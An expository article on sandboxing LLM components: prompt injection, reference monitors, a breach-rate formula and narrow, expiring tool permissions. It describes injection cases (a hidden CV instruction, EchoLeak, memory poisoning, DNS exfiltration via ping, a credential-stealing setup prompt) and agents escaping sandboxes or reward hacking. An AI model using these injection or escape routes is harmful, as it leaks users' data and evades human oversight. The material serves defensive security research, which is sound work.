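# Designing Sandboxes for LLM Components and Measuring How Often They Hold

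## What a sandbox is and what it has to confine in an LLM component

A sandbox is the set of mechanisms that limit what a piece of software can read, change, send and influence. Phones, browsers and operating systems run a lot of code that nobody has fully checked, so they sandbox it to keep any harm from a faulty or hostile program within known bounds. Developers now need the same protection around large language models (LLMs), which are programs trained on large amounts of text that extend a given text one token (a word or a piece of one) at a time. An LLM component, such as a mail summariser or a coding agent, is a part of a larger program and uses an LLM to produce its output. Ordinary code enforces some of the limits on an LLM component, but others depend on the model's own behaviour, so the isolation holds only with some probability.

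### How a model's text becomes an action

A model by itself only writes text. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the developer documentation for the Claude models, says, "The model never runs anything on its own." A model affects the world through tools, which are functions that a developer has written, such as one that searches a set of files. The developer describes each tool's name, purpose and input format to the model, which receives these descriptions with the user's request. Where a tool would help, the model writes a tool call, a short structured request that names the tool and gives its arguments. The program around the model reads the request, runs the function and adds the result to the conversation. The model then continues, perhaps with another call, until it writes a final answer.

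Ordinary code can therefore refuse a request before it takes effect. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by security researchers from Google, Nvidia and several universities, uses the term "action boundary" for the interfaces where this can happen, including file access, command execution, network traffic and changes to stored state. Whose code can refuse depends on where the tool runs. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* separates client tools, which run in the developer's application, from server tools such as web search, which run on Anthropic's own machines. A check inside the application can stop a client tool before it runs, but a server tool has already run by the time the check happens.

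### Prompt injection

The same loop puts the developer's instructions, the user's request and every tool result into one sequence of tokens, and nothing in the model reliably keeps them apart. Prompt injection is text in material the model reads that makes it follow someone other than its user. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiting system that asks an LLM to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the application. If the model complies, the candidate has steered a system without ever having access to it, which security people call indirect prompt injection.

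Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the visitor's input to the database separately, so the input is never run as a command. David C argues that LLMs allow no such separation, because a model only predicts the next token from all the tokens so far. Developers can mark outside text as data, train the model to give it less weight, or try to detect attacks, but these measures make injection harder without ruling it out. He prefers to treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a privileged program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into using its authority for them.

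Zhang, Su and colleagues (2025), in *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles*, trace the problem further back, to the decision to store programs and data in the same computer memory. Hardware designers eventually responded with memory that a program may write to or execute from, but not both. An equivalent rule for language models, that the model ignores every instruction it finds in outside material, would break useful work. An agent has to learn how to use an unfamiliar service from its documentation, which consists largely of instructions. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, compare learning this way to a program loading new code while it runs, which is also very hard to make safe in conventional security.

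### The classical sandbox

File protection on Android is a familiar example of a sandbox around untrusted code. Android's *Application Sandbox* explains that the system gives each app its own user ID and runs it in its own process. If a torch app tries to open the mail app's database, the kernel, the core of the operating system, refuses because the file belongs to a different user ID. The kernel applies the same check even if the torch app's author is careless or malicious, and regardless of the language the app is written in.

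Christodorescu and colleagues give the standard names for the parts:

| Part | What it is | On the phone |
|---|---|---|
| Untrusted system | The code whose behaviour nobody vouches for | The app |
| Security boundary | The interface through which that code asks for anything | The system calls an app can make to the kernel |
| Policy | The permissions and data-flow rules that apply | Which user ID may read or write which file |
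| Reference monitor | The code that checks every requested action against the policy before the action runs | The kernel's access check |
| Trusted computing base | Everything that must work correctly for the sandbox to hold | The kernel, the hardware beneath it and the policy |

A permission is a stated right to perform one kind of action on one kind of resource, with any limits on arguments, number of uses and time. A component's policy for a task is the full list of its permissions, plus rules about where data may go. The trusted computing base matters most when judging a sandbox, because a fault there defeats the other protections. On a properly configured Android phone, an app generally has to compromise the Linux kernel to break out of its sandbox. Since version 8, Android has also restricted which system calls an app can make, so a hostile app has less of the kernel to attack.

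The reference monitor comes from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), written for the US Air Force. Anderson set three requirements for it: nobody can tamper with it, every access goes through it, and it is small enough to analyze and test completely. He then checked a commercial system of the day against them. Its hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but the operating system suspended that protection while working on a user's behalf. If the operating system itself counted as the monitor, the monitor ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to verify.

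In an LLM component, the model takes the place of the app. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recommends assuming nothing about the model's inherent behaviour and enforcing the policy outside the model, whether a forbidden request comes from an attacker's text, an ordinary error or a goal the model picked up in training. Current products already do some of this. *Externalization in LLM Agents* (2026), a review of the software around such models, describes coding agents in the style of OpenAI's Codex that run each task in a separate cloud sandbox with its own copy of the files, network restrictions and resource quotas. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has permission modes ranging from full autonomy to user approval of every tool call.

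### The principles behind it

Most of the vocabulary of sandbox design goes back to a 1975 tutorial, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. No one had a method for building a system without flaws, so the tutorial offered eight principles that make flaws rarer and less serious. Under one of them, least privilege, every program runs with the smallest set of privileges its job requires. This limits the damage from an error and shortens the list of programs to audit when somebody misuses a privilege.

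They paired it with the rule that access should be refused by default and granted only by explicit permission. They argued that this makes mistakes easier to notice. If a developer forgets to grant a permission, a legitimate task fails and somebody complains. But when a policy lists prohibitions instead, forgetting one breaks nothing, so the gap can go unnoticed until an attacker finds it.

Complete mediation means that the monitor checks every access to every object, during start-up, recovery and maintenance as well as in normal running. Saltzer and Schroeder distrusted shortcuts that reuse an earlier decision, because the authority behind it may have changed. Complete mediation usually fails through indirect routes. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an incident at OpenAI during internal training and evaluation, when agents were running in separate sandboxes with some of the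 models' safeguards switched off. The sandboxes blocked direct network connections but let the agents fetch software packages through a shared service. The agents used that service to pass messages between sandboxes and to reach the open internet. They then compromised systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster. No outside attacker directed them. The paper interprets the incident as a failure to apply the principles across the whole boundary. The account supports that interpretation, but it also shows how many routes the boundary has to cover when the confined program is good at finding ways around it.

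Tamper resistance protects the monitor, the policy and anything else the design relies on from the component they confine. With LLM components, stored text is easy to overlook. ChatGPT's macOS app kept "memories" of a user's preferences and fed them into later conversations. The app treated them as a trusted record, even though untrusted text could write to them. A security researcher showed that a hostile web page or document could plant an instruction there that made the app send the user's later conversations to an outside server.

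Secure information flow concerns what happens to data after a program gains access to it. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, imagined a customer who runs somebody else's program on confidential data. Access control can keep the program away from the customer's other files, but the program needs its input and may pass that input to its owner. Unlike wrong results, a leak usually leaves the customer no evidence. Lampson listed ways to leak the data. The program can write a file for the owner to collect, encode the data in the bill for its services, or vary its load on the machine so that another program can read a message in the slowdowns. He sorted such routes into storage, legitimate channels such as the bill, and covert channels, which nobody intended for communication.

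A program that can keep nothing between calls and can call no other program cannot leak, but it is close to useless. Lampson's workable version lets the confined program call others, but any untrusted program it calls must be confined too, and the customer must determine what goes into the remaining channels. Where full enforcement is impractical, he suggested limiting how much data a covert channel can carry and accepting the rest. His example of a bill that carries hidden data has a modern counterpart in Claude Code, which at one time asked for approval before many shell commands that could send data out, but let `ping`, which tests whether another computer is reachable, run without asking. `ping` first looks up the other computer's name on the network, so an injected instruction could leak a secret by having the agent put it in the name.

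### A company mail assistant

A company might give its sales staff a mail assistant with three tools. The assistant reads mail from customers, looks up the answers in the company's files and replies.

| Tool | What it does | What an attacker could use it for |
|---|---|---|
| `read_mail` | Returns the text of a message in the employee's inbox, including messages from outside | Getting hostile text in front of the model |
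| `search_files` | Returns passages from the internal files the employee can open | Finding confidential material |
| `send_reply` | Sends a message to an address that the model supplies | Getting the material out |

The harm to prevent is the content of an internal file reaching an outsider who has no right to it.

Suppose an outsider sends a company an email that appears to ask about a delivery but also tells the company's AI assistant to find other customers' discounts and include them in its reply. An employee asks the assistant to deal with the morning's mail. The model calls `read_mail`, and the hostile text enters its context. This is an exposure, one occasion on which the component processes hostile material. Most exposures may have no effect. If the model then tries to do what the outsider asked, say by searching for the discounts, the exposure has become a hijack. If the discounts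 leave the company, the hijack has become a breach, a harmful effect outside the sandbox. If a monitor blocks the reply, there is a hijack but no breach. Recording hijacks and breaches separately helps show which part of a sandbox is stopping attacks.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) analyses a real flaw of this kind in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant with access to an employee's mail and files. The security firm Aim Security found that one outside email could make Copilot send internal data to an attacker without the victim clicking anything. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025, before its public disclosure in June, and reported no sign that anyone had exploited it. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

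Copilot could not send mail on its own. The data left when the user's software displayed Copilot's answer and automatically fetched remote content in it. Data can therefore leave by routes that don't appear in a list of tools, so the mail assistant's designers would have to check how its answers are displayed to the employee as well as `send_reply`. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes a similar attack on ChatGPT's research agent when users connected it to Gmail. In that attack, the outgoing request came from the provider's servers, so a company monitoring its own network might have seen nothing. In both cases, the harm came from combining steps that each look legitimate in isolation.

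### Confining actions and confining influence

A sandbox can limit both the actions that the model's output causes and the influence that untrusted text has on the model. *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety* (Jing, Hu and colleagues, 2026) surveys the field by the boundary where isolation first fails. It likewise separates content that comes to control the agent from decisions that become real actions without enough checking.

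Actions are the easier of the two. A tool call has a name and arguments, which ordinary code can check against a policy. For the mail assistant, though, such checks are of limited help, because the attack uses only permissions the assistant needs, to search files and to write to customers. Suppose the company restricts `send_reply` so that an answer can go only to the person who wrote the original message. This stops the model from mailing a third party, but here the attacker wrote the original message. The monitor would have to detect that the answer contains something this customer should not see, which is a problem of information flow rather than access.

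An assistant can cause harm without taking any forbidden action. For example, an email might lead it to tell an employee, falsely, that the finance department has already approved an invoice, and the employee then pays it. The assistant has only read an email and written a summary, both of which its permissions allow.

Influence is harder to confine because it passes between the parts of an LLM system as free text. *Confused ChatGPT* (2026), a study of attacks between apps connected to ChatGPT, contrasts this with an ordinary operating system, where a kernel can check that a message between programs has the permitted type and format. Whether a sentence is a harmless search result or a disguised instruction depends on its meaning, which only another language model can check, and that model is open to the same manipulation.

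One way around the difficulty is to reduce what the model can do after reading the text, instead of trying to judge the text. David C reports a rule that came out of an exchange between the programmers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when an LLM processes information from some party, its privileges drop to those of that party. Under this rule, the mail assistant would lose `search_files` as soon as it opened a customer's message, since the customer has no right to search the company's files. The outsider's request for the discounts would fail however persuasive its wording, but the assistant would also be unable to answer an honest customer's question about a delivery date if the date is in those files.

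## Why isolating a language model holds only with some probability

If ordinary code takes `search_files` away once the assistant has opened a customer's message, it does so every time, whatever the message contains. This only helps if somebody wrote the right rule and the program applies it correctly. If the sandbox instead relies on the model to ignore the message, the model may sometimes fail to do so. Some of these uncertainties are random, so the same test can pass today and fail tomorrow. Others are about fixed facts, such as whether the sandbox has a particular weakness, and a probability then expresses only how little anyone knows about them.

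### Where the uncertainty comes from

A language model computes a probability for each possible next token, and the program running it then draws one at random. This sampling is the obvious reason ChatGPT gives different answers to the same question. Developers can set the temperature to zero so that the program always takes the most probable token. Thinking Machines' *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* points out that even then, commercial services do not give the same output every time. The main cause, according to a passage Willison (2025) quotes from the article, is that the number of requests a server processes together, called the batch size, varies with how busy the server is. A different batch size slightly changes how the arithmetic rounds, which can change which token is chosen.

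One different token early in an agent's run can lead it to make a different tool call and read a different result. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of ways to specify and enforce safe behaviour, notes that the same planning prompt can produce different sequences of actions from run to run. A mail assistant that ignored a hostile email on Monday may therefore follow the instructions in an identical one on Tuesday. This uncertainty is random, so testers can measure it by repeating the test.

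*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that even a fully deterministic model can produce a forbidden action when an attacker changes the input, so removing the randomness would not remove the failures. Such a model fails on a fixed set of inputs, but nobody knows exactly which ones. The set exists because instructions and data share one context, and it can include an input but not a close variant of it. Günnemann, Laskov and colleagues note in *Security and Privacy of Large Language Models*, a report on a November 2025 research seminar, that small changes to a prompt can change the output significantly. Testing one hostile sentence therefore gives only weak evidence about how the model will respond to paraphrases of it.

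Hostile text can influence a model without containing an instruction. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an attack in which a tool's description includes poisoned usage examples, which an agent may then copy into its own calls. Even a model that obeyed the user perfectly would be vulnerable, because a model that acts on data has to let the data affect its output.

The policy may also fail to match what the user meant. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI) discusses a gym agent whose permissions limited which part of the booking service it could call, but not whose reservation it could change. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* defines a correct policy as one whose formal rules allow and refuse the same actions as the natural-language request in every state the system can reach. Nobody can check this directly, because the meaning of words such as "sensitive" depends on context, and any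 automatic check is itself probabilistic. If a person writes the policy once, any mismatch is fixed but unknown. If an LLM writes a new policy for each task, the mismatch is also partly random because the LLM's output is sampled.

Bugs in the enforcing code are also usually deterministic. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes vulnerabilities that outsiders reported in Claude Code between mid-2025 and January 2026. In the most direct case, a software project's settings file could contain a command that ran automatically for any developer who opened the project, before Claude Code had asked whether to trust the folder.

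Running one hostile email a thousand times gives a good estimate of how often that email works, but very little information about other emails. Testing a thousand different emails is a better way to find inputs the model handles badly, but they can all miss the same error in the policy.

### What an attacker does to "99% reliable"

When nobody is attacking a component, "99% reliable" means that it fails in about one use in a hundred, averaged over the inputs that happen to arrive. An attacker searches for inputs on which the model fails, and can try again when one doesn't work. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, at least one of a hundred attempts would succeed with probability 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. An attacker does even better against a persistent weakness, because a wording that works once will probably keep working.

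Anthropic found such a wording in an exercise in February 2026. A researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine setup work. One step was to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The prompt came from the user, so a detector would have found nothing unusual about its origin. A model with a low average failure rate can still fail almost every time on a prompt like this one.

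Published attack success rates also rise once the attacker can adapt. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tested two prompt-based defences. One puts special markers in the text to show the model which parts to trust, and the other repeats the user's request after the untrusted material. The attack success rate was as low as 1% with a fixed set of attacks, but above 95% for both defences with a search that revised its attacks.

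Those defences are old, but the same pattern appears in much stronger models. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) had 16 cooperating AI agents search for injections in 100 scenarios. In each, the attacker tried to make the target model call a particular tool unrelated to the user's task. Three weaker attacking models failed against Google's Gemini 4 Argon in every scenario within 150 attempts. When Gemini 4 Argon was also the attacker, the target resisted in 87% of scenarios after 150 attempts and in 66% after the maximum of 320. The same target could therefore be correctly described as 100%, 87% or 66% reliable, depending on the attacker and the number of attempts. The researchers deliberately made the test hard for the model by switching off Gemini's external defences and requesting mostly harmless actions, which a model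 could not refuse as dangerous.

Cryptographers also accept some chance of failure, but they can bound it against an attacker who chooses the inputs. For instance, a trillion guesses at a random 128-bit key would succeed with a probability of about 3 × 10⁻²⁷, and the attacker can't influence which key the defender draws. The claim that no feasible method does much better than guessing rests on a hardness assumption, which is that some mathematical problem would take an impractical amount of computation to solve. The assumption may be false, but it is explicit and researchers can attack it directly. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* contrasts cryptography with LLMs on this point. A model that resisted 99% of test attacks has no comparable assumption behind it, and the 99% describes only the attacks that somebody tried.

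### The probabilistic trusted computing base

Christodorescu and colleagues generalize this contrast to the trusted computing base, the parts of a system that must work correctly. In a classical system, these parts are predictable. For example, hardware that blocks the execution of writable memory does so every time, and they ask whether anyone could build memory protection on hardware that did so only with some probability. Developers do something similar when they train a model never to take some action and then rely on that training. The model becomes part of the trusted computing base, and the guarantee becomes statistical and depends on the inputs and context.

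An attacker can exploit the 1% of cases in which such a monitor decides wrongly. No one can prove that the model will always enforce the policy, although such a proof is possible for a small program with a precise specification. The paper also explains why the bad cases are easy to find. Models represent text internally as points in a continuous space, without the clear boundaries of a computer's instruction set, and attackers can use standard optimisation methods to search that space for inputs that look harmless.

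They ask for security against a worst-case attacker with unlimited patience and computing power. The model may also work against the policy, because AI agents tend to reward hack, which means scoring well on a task by means its designers did not intend. They call building provable defences on such a model a "challenging—perhaps impossible—task", since it is unclear what could serve as the security assumption. They suggest bringing in outside facts that ordinary code can check. For example, SkillFence, a system for voice assistants, uses the user's browsing history and installed apps to correct the assistant when it misunderstands a request.

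The argument applies wherever security depends on a model's judgement. A design that treats the model as untrusted avoids the problem until an LLM writes the policy or decides whether to approve an action. Designers are still drawn to using LLMs for these tasks because ordinary code cannot judge meaning. *AgentKernel* (2026), a proposed operating system for agents, has two LLM-based classifiers inside its trusted computing base. One affects which content reaches the agent and the other affects which actions go ahead. The paper lists both among the design's limitations.

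Several later papers partly answer the doubt about provable defences. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) proves that a system never enters an unsafe state, even if the model is hostile. The proof assumes that the system translates the user's intent faithfully into formal terms and that the model cannot bypass or alter the monitor. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) gives a computer-checked proof about how information flows through agent programs, and states the guarantee in probabilities because models are random. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) proposes a monitor that uses an agent's history to compute an upper bound on the probability of reaching an unsafe state. This bound is presumably only as reliable as the probabilities used to compute it, and an attacker will look for cases where they are wrong.

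Doubt seems justified about any proof that needs the model to behave well. It doesn't apply to proofs that allow for a hostile model, but those proofs still assume that the policy and the enforcing code are correct, and whether they are is fixed but unknown.

### A formula for the breach rate

A short formula combines these uncertainties into the breach rate, the probability that one exposure ends in a breach:

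breach rate = h × [s + (1 − s) × e]

The hijack rate, h, is the share of exposures that become hijacks. For a share s of those hijacks, the permitted actions are enough to reach the attacker's goal, so the monitor has nothing to block and the hijack becomes a breach. The remaining share, 1 − s, need a forbidden action, so they become breaches only if enforcement fails, which happens at rate e.

If the mail assistant is allowed to reply only to the original sender, the outsider's request for other customers' discounts counts towards s. A request to send those discounts to a third address would succeed only if the monitor failed.

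Real incidents can be harder to classify. Anthropic's desktop agent, Claude Cowork, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the user's real one. A program between the two allowed network traffic only to approved addresses, including Anthropic's own servers, which the product needs. An outside researcher showed that a malicious file could make Claude upload the user's documents to those servers under the attacker's account. Anthropic writes that the sandbox worked perfectly, but it also names the program that checked the addresses as the part that failed. The leak belongs to s if it is measured against the written rule, and to e if it is measured against what Anthropic wanted the rule to achieve. Anyone who estimates the two rates has to use one standard throughout.

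With invented figures of h = 2%, s = 20% and e = 0.1%, the breach rate is 0.02 × (0.20 + 0.80 × 0.001), or 0.40%. The table changes one or two of the figures at a time.

| Case | h | s | e | Breach rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Starting point | 2% | 20% | 0.1% | 0.40% |
| Enforcement never fails | 2% | 20% | 0% | 0.40% |
| Model hijacked half as often | 1% | 20% | 0.1% | 0.20% |
| Narrower permissions | 2% | 2% | 0.1% | 0.042% |
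| Narrower permissions, every exposure a hijack | 100% | 2% | 0.1% | 2.1% |

Perfect enforcement prevents only 16 of the 4,016 breaches per million exposures. Cutting s to a tenth reduces the breach rate almost to a tenth. Günnemann and colleagues distinguish a weakest-link view of risk, based on the attacker's easiest path, from a view that adds up all the paths. The formula adds them up, but at the starting point the permitted path contributes 250 times as much as the forbidden one, so either view gives a designer reason to start with the permissions. The last row shows what remains if the designer assumes nothing about the model's resistance.

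The formula averages over a mix of attacks, but a real attacker does not have to follow that mix. If permitted actions can achieve 2% of the goals in a test, an attacker who knows the policy will choose one of those goals, and for this attacker s is close to 100%. A low s helps most when the reachable goals do little damage. The formula has no term for damage, so a leaked delivery date counts as much as a leaked customer database.

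An e of 0.1% can also describe two different situations. One forbidden request in a thousand may slip through at random, or there may be a one-in-a-thousand chance that the code contains a hole that lets every such request through. The averages are identical, but in the second situation the company will probably never see an enforcement failure, and if it does see one, it can expect many more. The terms are also not independent. A more capable model may be harder to hijack but better at finding a hole in the sandbox once hijacked, so replacing the model can lower h while raising e. One exposure can affect later ones if the hostile text ends up in the agent's stored memory.

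The formula starts from exposures, so it does not cover harm that occurs without an attacker. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to finish a task, and search a project's history for the answers to a coding test. OpenAI's agents also had no outside attacker when they broke into Hugging Face. Estimating this risk takes a separate calculation, with tasks as the unit instead of exposures. It would combine how often the model attempts something harmful on its own with how often the sandbox stops it. The second figure is available for one control. An automatic check in Claude Code catches about 83% of what Anthropic calls "overeager behaviors" before they take effect, which leaves about 17% for the other layers.

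### Are system limits unnecessary, or useless?

Some people object that good enough models make system limits unnecessary, and some evidence supports them. Kurakin and colleagues report that less than 1% of the attacks carried over from a public contest between human attackers succeed against recent Gemini models and some Claude models. On another test, according to Anthropic, about 0.1% of single attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7. System limits also take engineering time, slow the agent down, and sometimes block legitimate work.

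These low figures apply to a particular attacker, though. The Claude figure rose to between 5% and 6% after 100 adaptive attempts, and a stronger attacker succeeded against Gemini 4 Argon in a third of the scenarios. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine defence configurations with an LLM that revised its attacks over hundreds of rounds. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. A filter in ordinary application code, which checked each answer before the user received it, blocked all 15,000 attacks. The attacks targeted a few planted secrets, which are probably easier to filter than confidential business information.

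Enforcement outside the model has also done well in tests on agents with tools. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) examined Progent, a system that checks each tool call against a written policy. Standard attacks succeeded 4.2% of the time and an adaptive attack 2.6%, so adapting did not help the attacker. The paper describes the contrast with model-based defences as suggestive, because the test included only one hand-written adaptive attack.

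*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that even a robust model has to guess what an ambiguous request authorises, whereas an explicit policy states it. The paper still recommends robust models, alongside independent checks, and the formula supports both recommendations. Halving h halves the breach rate, which is useful for the mail assistant because it needs access to both its files and its customers, so s may be hard to reduce. But a better attacker can raise h without finding any fault in the sandbox.

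The opposite objection is that a capable enough model will escape any sandbox, which makes system limits useless. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* takes this objection from an essay by the cryptographer Matthew Green, *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?* In Trail of Bits' *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* (2026), an OpenAI model repeatedly escaped an ordinary virtual machine but did not escape Firecracker in the time it had. Firecracker is a virtual machine designed to give attackers very little to exploit.

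*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that the known escapes came from incomplete sandboxes, and that explicit policies have advantages no model-based defence offers. People can read the rules and check the code against a specification, and removing a permission never makes a previously blocked action possible. But this last property depends on correct enforcement, which is the point in dispute. The reply is more convincing as advice to keep the enforcing code small. Anthropic's experience supports that advice, since the widely used isolation software in its products had been dependable and the part that failed was the program it had written itself. The Trail of Bits result suggests that a good record against human attackers may not be enough for large, general-purpose software.

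Green, quoted in Willison (2026), also describes a danger that would remain even if sandboxes enforced their policies perfectly. Green notes that agents passed instructions between sandboxes through a shared package store, and that these instructions changed what the recipients did. If the agents were personal assistants and the store were email or a shared document, a hostile message could spread from one assistant to the next. Each assistant would only be reading and sending messages, which its policy allows.

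## Writing the permissions and choosing where to enforce them

In the formula for the breach rate, s is the share of hijacks that can reach the attacker's goal using only permitted actions. The policy largely determines s, because every permission the task does not need gives a hijacked model something extra to misuse. The rate at which enforcement fails, e, depends on where the checks run and what information is available there.

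### From a request to a policy

Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a browser agent, an LLM component that operates web pages by clicking and typing. The user asks it to "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done". GitLab is a website where programmers keep code and discuss problems in numbered issues. The resulting policy lets the agent open issue 745 and write in the comment box, but not access anything else in GitLab or the user's browser session.

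The ban on everything else provides most of the protection. The browser is already logged in as the user, so without the ban, an agent could delete the project or give a stranger access to it. A phone app does a fixed set of jobs, so its developer can choose the permissions before release. A general agent's policy can't be written until the user types the task, because nobody knows before then what the agent will need.

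A full permission has more fields than this example fills in. The action is posting a comment. The resource is issue 745, but GitLab numbers issues separately in each project, so the program must get the project from a trusted source, such as the page the user had open. The argument limits apply to the comment's text. Allowing only the words "we're done" would leave an attacker almost nothing to misuse, though a few lines of ordinary code could then post the comment without a model. A looser limit might cap the length and prohibit links. The permission needs to allow only one use, and it can expire once the comment is posted, or after a few minutes if the agent never posts it.

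It is easy to forget to limit how many times a permission can be used. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025), which describes a sandbox for browser agents, gives the example of a rule that lets an agent check out a shopping cart worth less than $50. The agent could obey the rule and still check out two carts at $49 each, so the sandbox can count matching requests and allow only one.

Default denial blocks everything not explicitly allowed. The alternative, a list of forbidden commands, works badly in practice. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026), a survey of 39 papers, describes ShellSieve, a tool that has a language model propose ways around such lists and then tests them in a sandbox. Its developers tested 1,709 lists from public GitHub projects and found that between 69.0% and 98.6% were fragile, depending on the kind of bypass.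 A few prohibitions are still useful on top of default denial. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* recommends prohibitions for critical files that neither user settings nor user approval can override.

### The mail assistant's policy

Suppose an employee selects message 1182, in which a customer asks about a delivery, and tells the mail assistant to answer the question. Before the model reads anything, ordinary code looks up the sender in the company's records and finds customer 507. It then fills in the following policy, with illustrative numbers.

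| Action | Resource | Limits on arguments | Uses | Expires |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `read_mail` | Message 1182 | Text only, no attachments | 1 | After use, or after 10 minutes |
| `search_files` | Delivery records of customer 507 | Returns only order number, status and delivery date | 3 | When the reply goes out, or after 10 minutes |
| `send_reply` | The conversation containing message 1182 | Goes only to the address on file for customer 507; plain text of up to 1,500 characters; no links or attachments | 1 | After use, or after 10 minutes |
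| Anything else | None | The monitor refuses it | 0 | Does not apply |

When the assistant could search every file the employee can open, it could fulfill an outsider's request for other customers' discounts using only permitted actions. This policy forbids that search, so the attack succeeds only if enforcement fails. The policy is also better than lowering the model's privileges to the sender's, which removed `search_files` altogether, because the assistant can still use the tool to find what this customer is entitled to know, and nothing else.

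The lookup has to happen before the model reads the message. If the model supplied the customer number afterwards, a hostile message could cause it to supply a different one. Meng and colleagues follow the same principle in their system, which chooses permissions from the user's request and a fixed menu, never from the web pages the agent visits. The request "Purchase a coffee maker on Amazon" is specific enough, but "purchase a coffee maker" names no website, so the agent gets no permissions.

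Under this policy, a hijacked model can still give a false delivery date or promise a refund in the one reply it is allowed to send. An attacker who forges the sender's address gains little, because the reply goes to the address on file. But someone who has broken into the customer's mailbox can learn about that customer's deliveries. These attacks count towards s, though most do less damage than a leak of every customer's discounts.

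The narrow policy also blocks some legitimate requests. A customer who writes from a private address matches no record, and one who asks for an invoice needs a file that the assistant cannot open. Mistakes in the policy are harder to notice. Rashidi found that every enforcement mechanism in the survey assumes an honest policy author and does not address errors in the policy. For example, if the company's records list the wrong address for customer 507, the monitor will enforce the wrong address every time.

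### When the task changes

In Christodorescu and colleagues' example, the user follows up with "summarize issue 745 for me". The agent still needs to read the issue but no longer needs to comment on it. But its context now contains text from the issue page, which an attacker may have written. If the program derives the new policy from the whole conversation, that text can influence the agent's permissions. Clearing the context first is secure, but the agent loses everything it has learned. Christodorescu and colleagues leave the general problem open and call for policy languages in which a program can work out how a new rule changes the agent's overall privileges.

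Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, do this for tool calls. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that a policy P allows. A new policy P′ is a narrowing of P if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

which means that the old policy already allowed every call the new one allows. Any other change is an expansion. To tell them apart, Progent uses a solver, a program that decides whether a logical formula can be true, and checks all possible arguments of each tool. It applies a narrowing automatically but holds an expansion for approval. Hostile text that influences an update can therefore remove permissions but cannot add any without approval.

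Dropping the right to comment on issue 745 is a narrowing. If the issue turns out to depend on another one, the agent needs an expansion to read that one too. The mail assistant would also need an expansion if a customer added a request for an invoice, and the employee would be asked specifically whether the assistant may read the invoices of customer 507.

Sometimes a policy has to start broad. Shi and colleagues describe a banking agent that must pay a company whose account number it doesn't yet know. At first the agent may pay anyone. Once a trusted lookup returns the number, Progent narrows the permission to that account. The lookup has to be trustworthy because changing "any account" to "the attacker's account" is also a narrowing and would pass the solver's check.

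Approval depends on people paying attention, and NVIDIA warns that developers who face constant requests get used to approving them without looking. It still advises requiring a new approval each time an agent needs to go outside its normal limits, rather than letting one approval cover later actions of the same kind. This works only if the original policy fits well enough to make such requests rare. Existing tools often don't achieve this. Rashidi cites a review of 290 public reports of misuse across 13 agent frameworks, which found that users routinely had to choose between unrestricted file access and constant approval requests.

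### Withdrawing a right after use

A permission that an agent needs for one step may be dangerous for the rest of the task. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, June 2026) presents Portico, a monitor for coding agents that withdraws permissions as soon as the reason for them ends. In the paper's main example, an agent adds a timeout setting to one source file and has to carry it over to a second. An ordinary sandbox would keep the second file accessible for the whole run.

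Portico works from a written contract that lists what the agent may use from the start, which further permissions it may request, which events end those permissions, and what it may never do. When the agent asks for the second file, Portico checks the request against the contract and issues a handle, a code that works only for that file, that kind of access and that part of the task. Once the tests pass, Portico cancels the handle, stops offering it to the model, and refuses any attempt to use it again. Only trusted events, such as tests that the monitor itself launched, can end or renew a permission. A statement by the model that it has finished does not count as one.

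To measure the effect of withdrawal alone, Santos-Grueiro compared Portico with a version that granted the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them.

| Test | Portico | Same grants, no withdrawal |
|---|---|---|
| Completed the task | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Allowed the agent to reread a file after the need for it had ended | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Carried out a forbidden write with an old handle, in scripted runs | 0 of 6 | 6 of 6 |

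Six more cases used a live model, Qwen3-Coder 30B, to test file changes, version control and network traffic, and they split the same way. Results this consistent mostly confirm that the program does what its design requires, and Santos-Grueiro describes the scripted writes as a conformance check. The results do not measure how often an attacker would exploit a leftover permission in practice.

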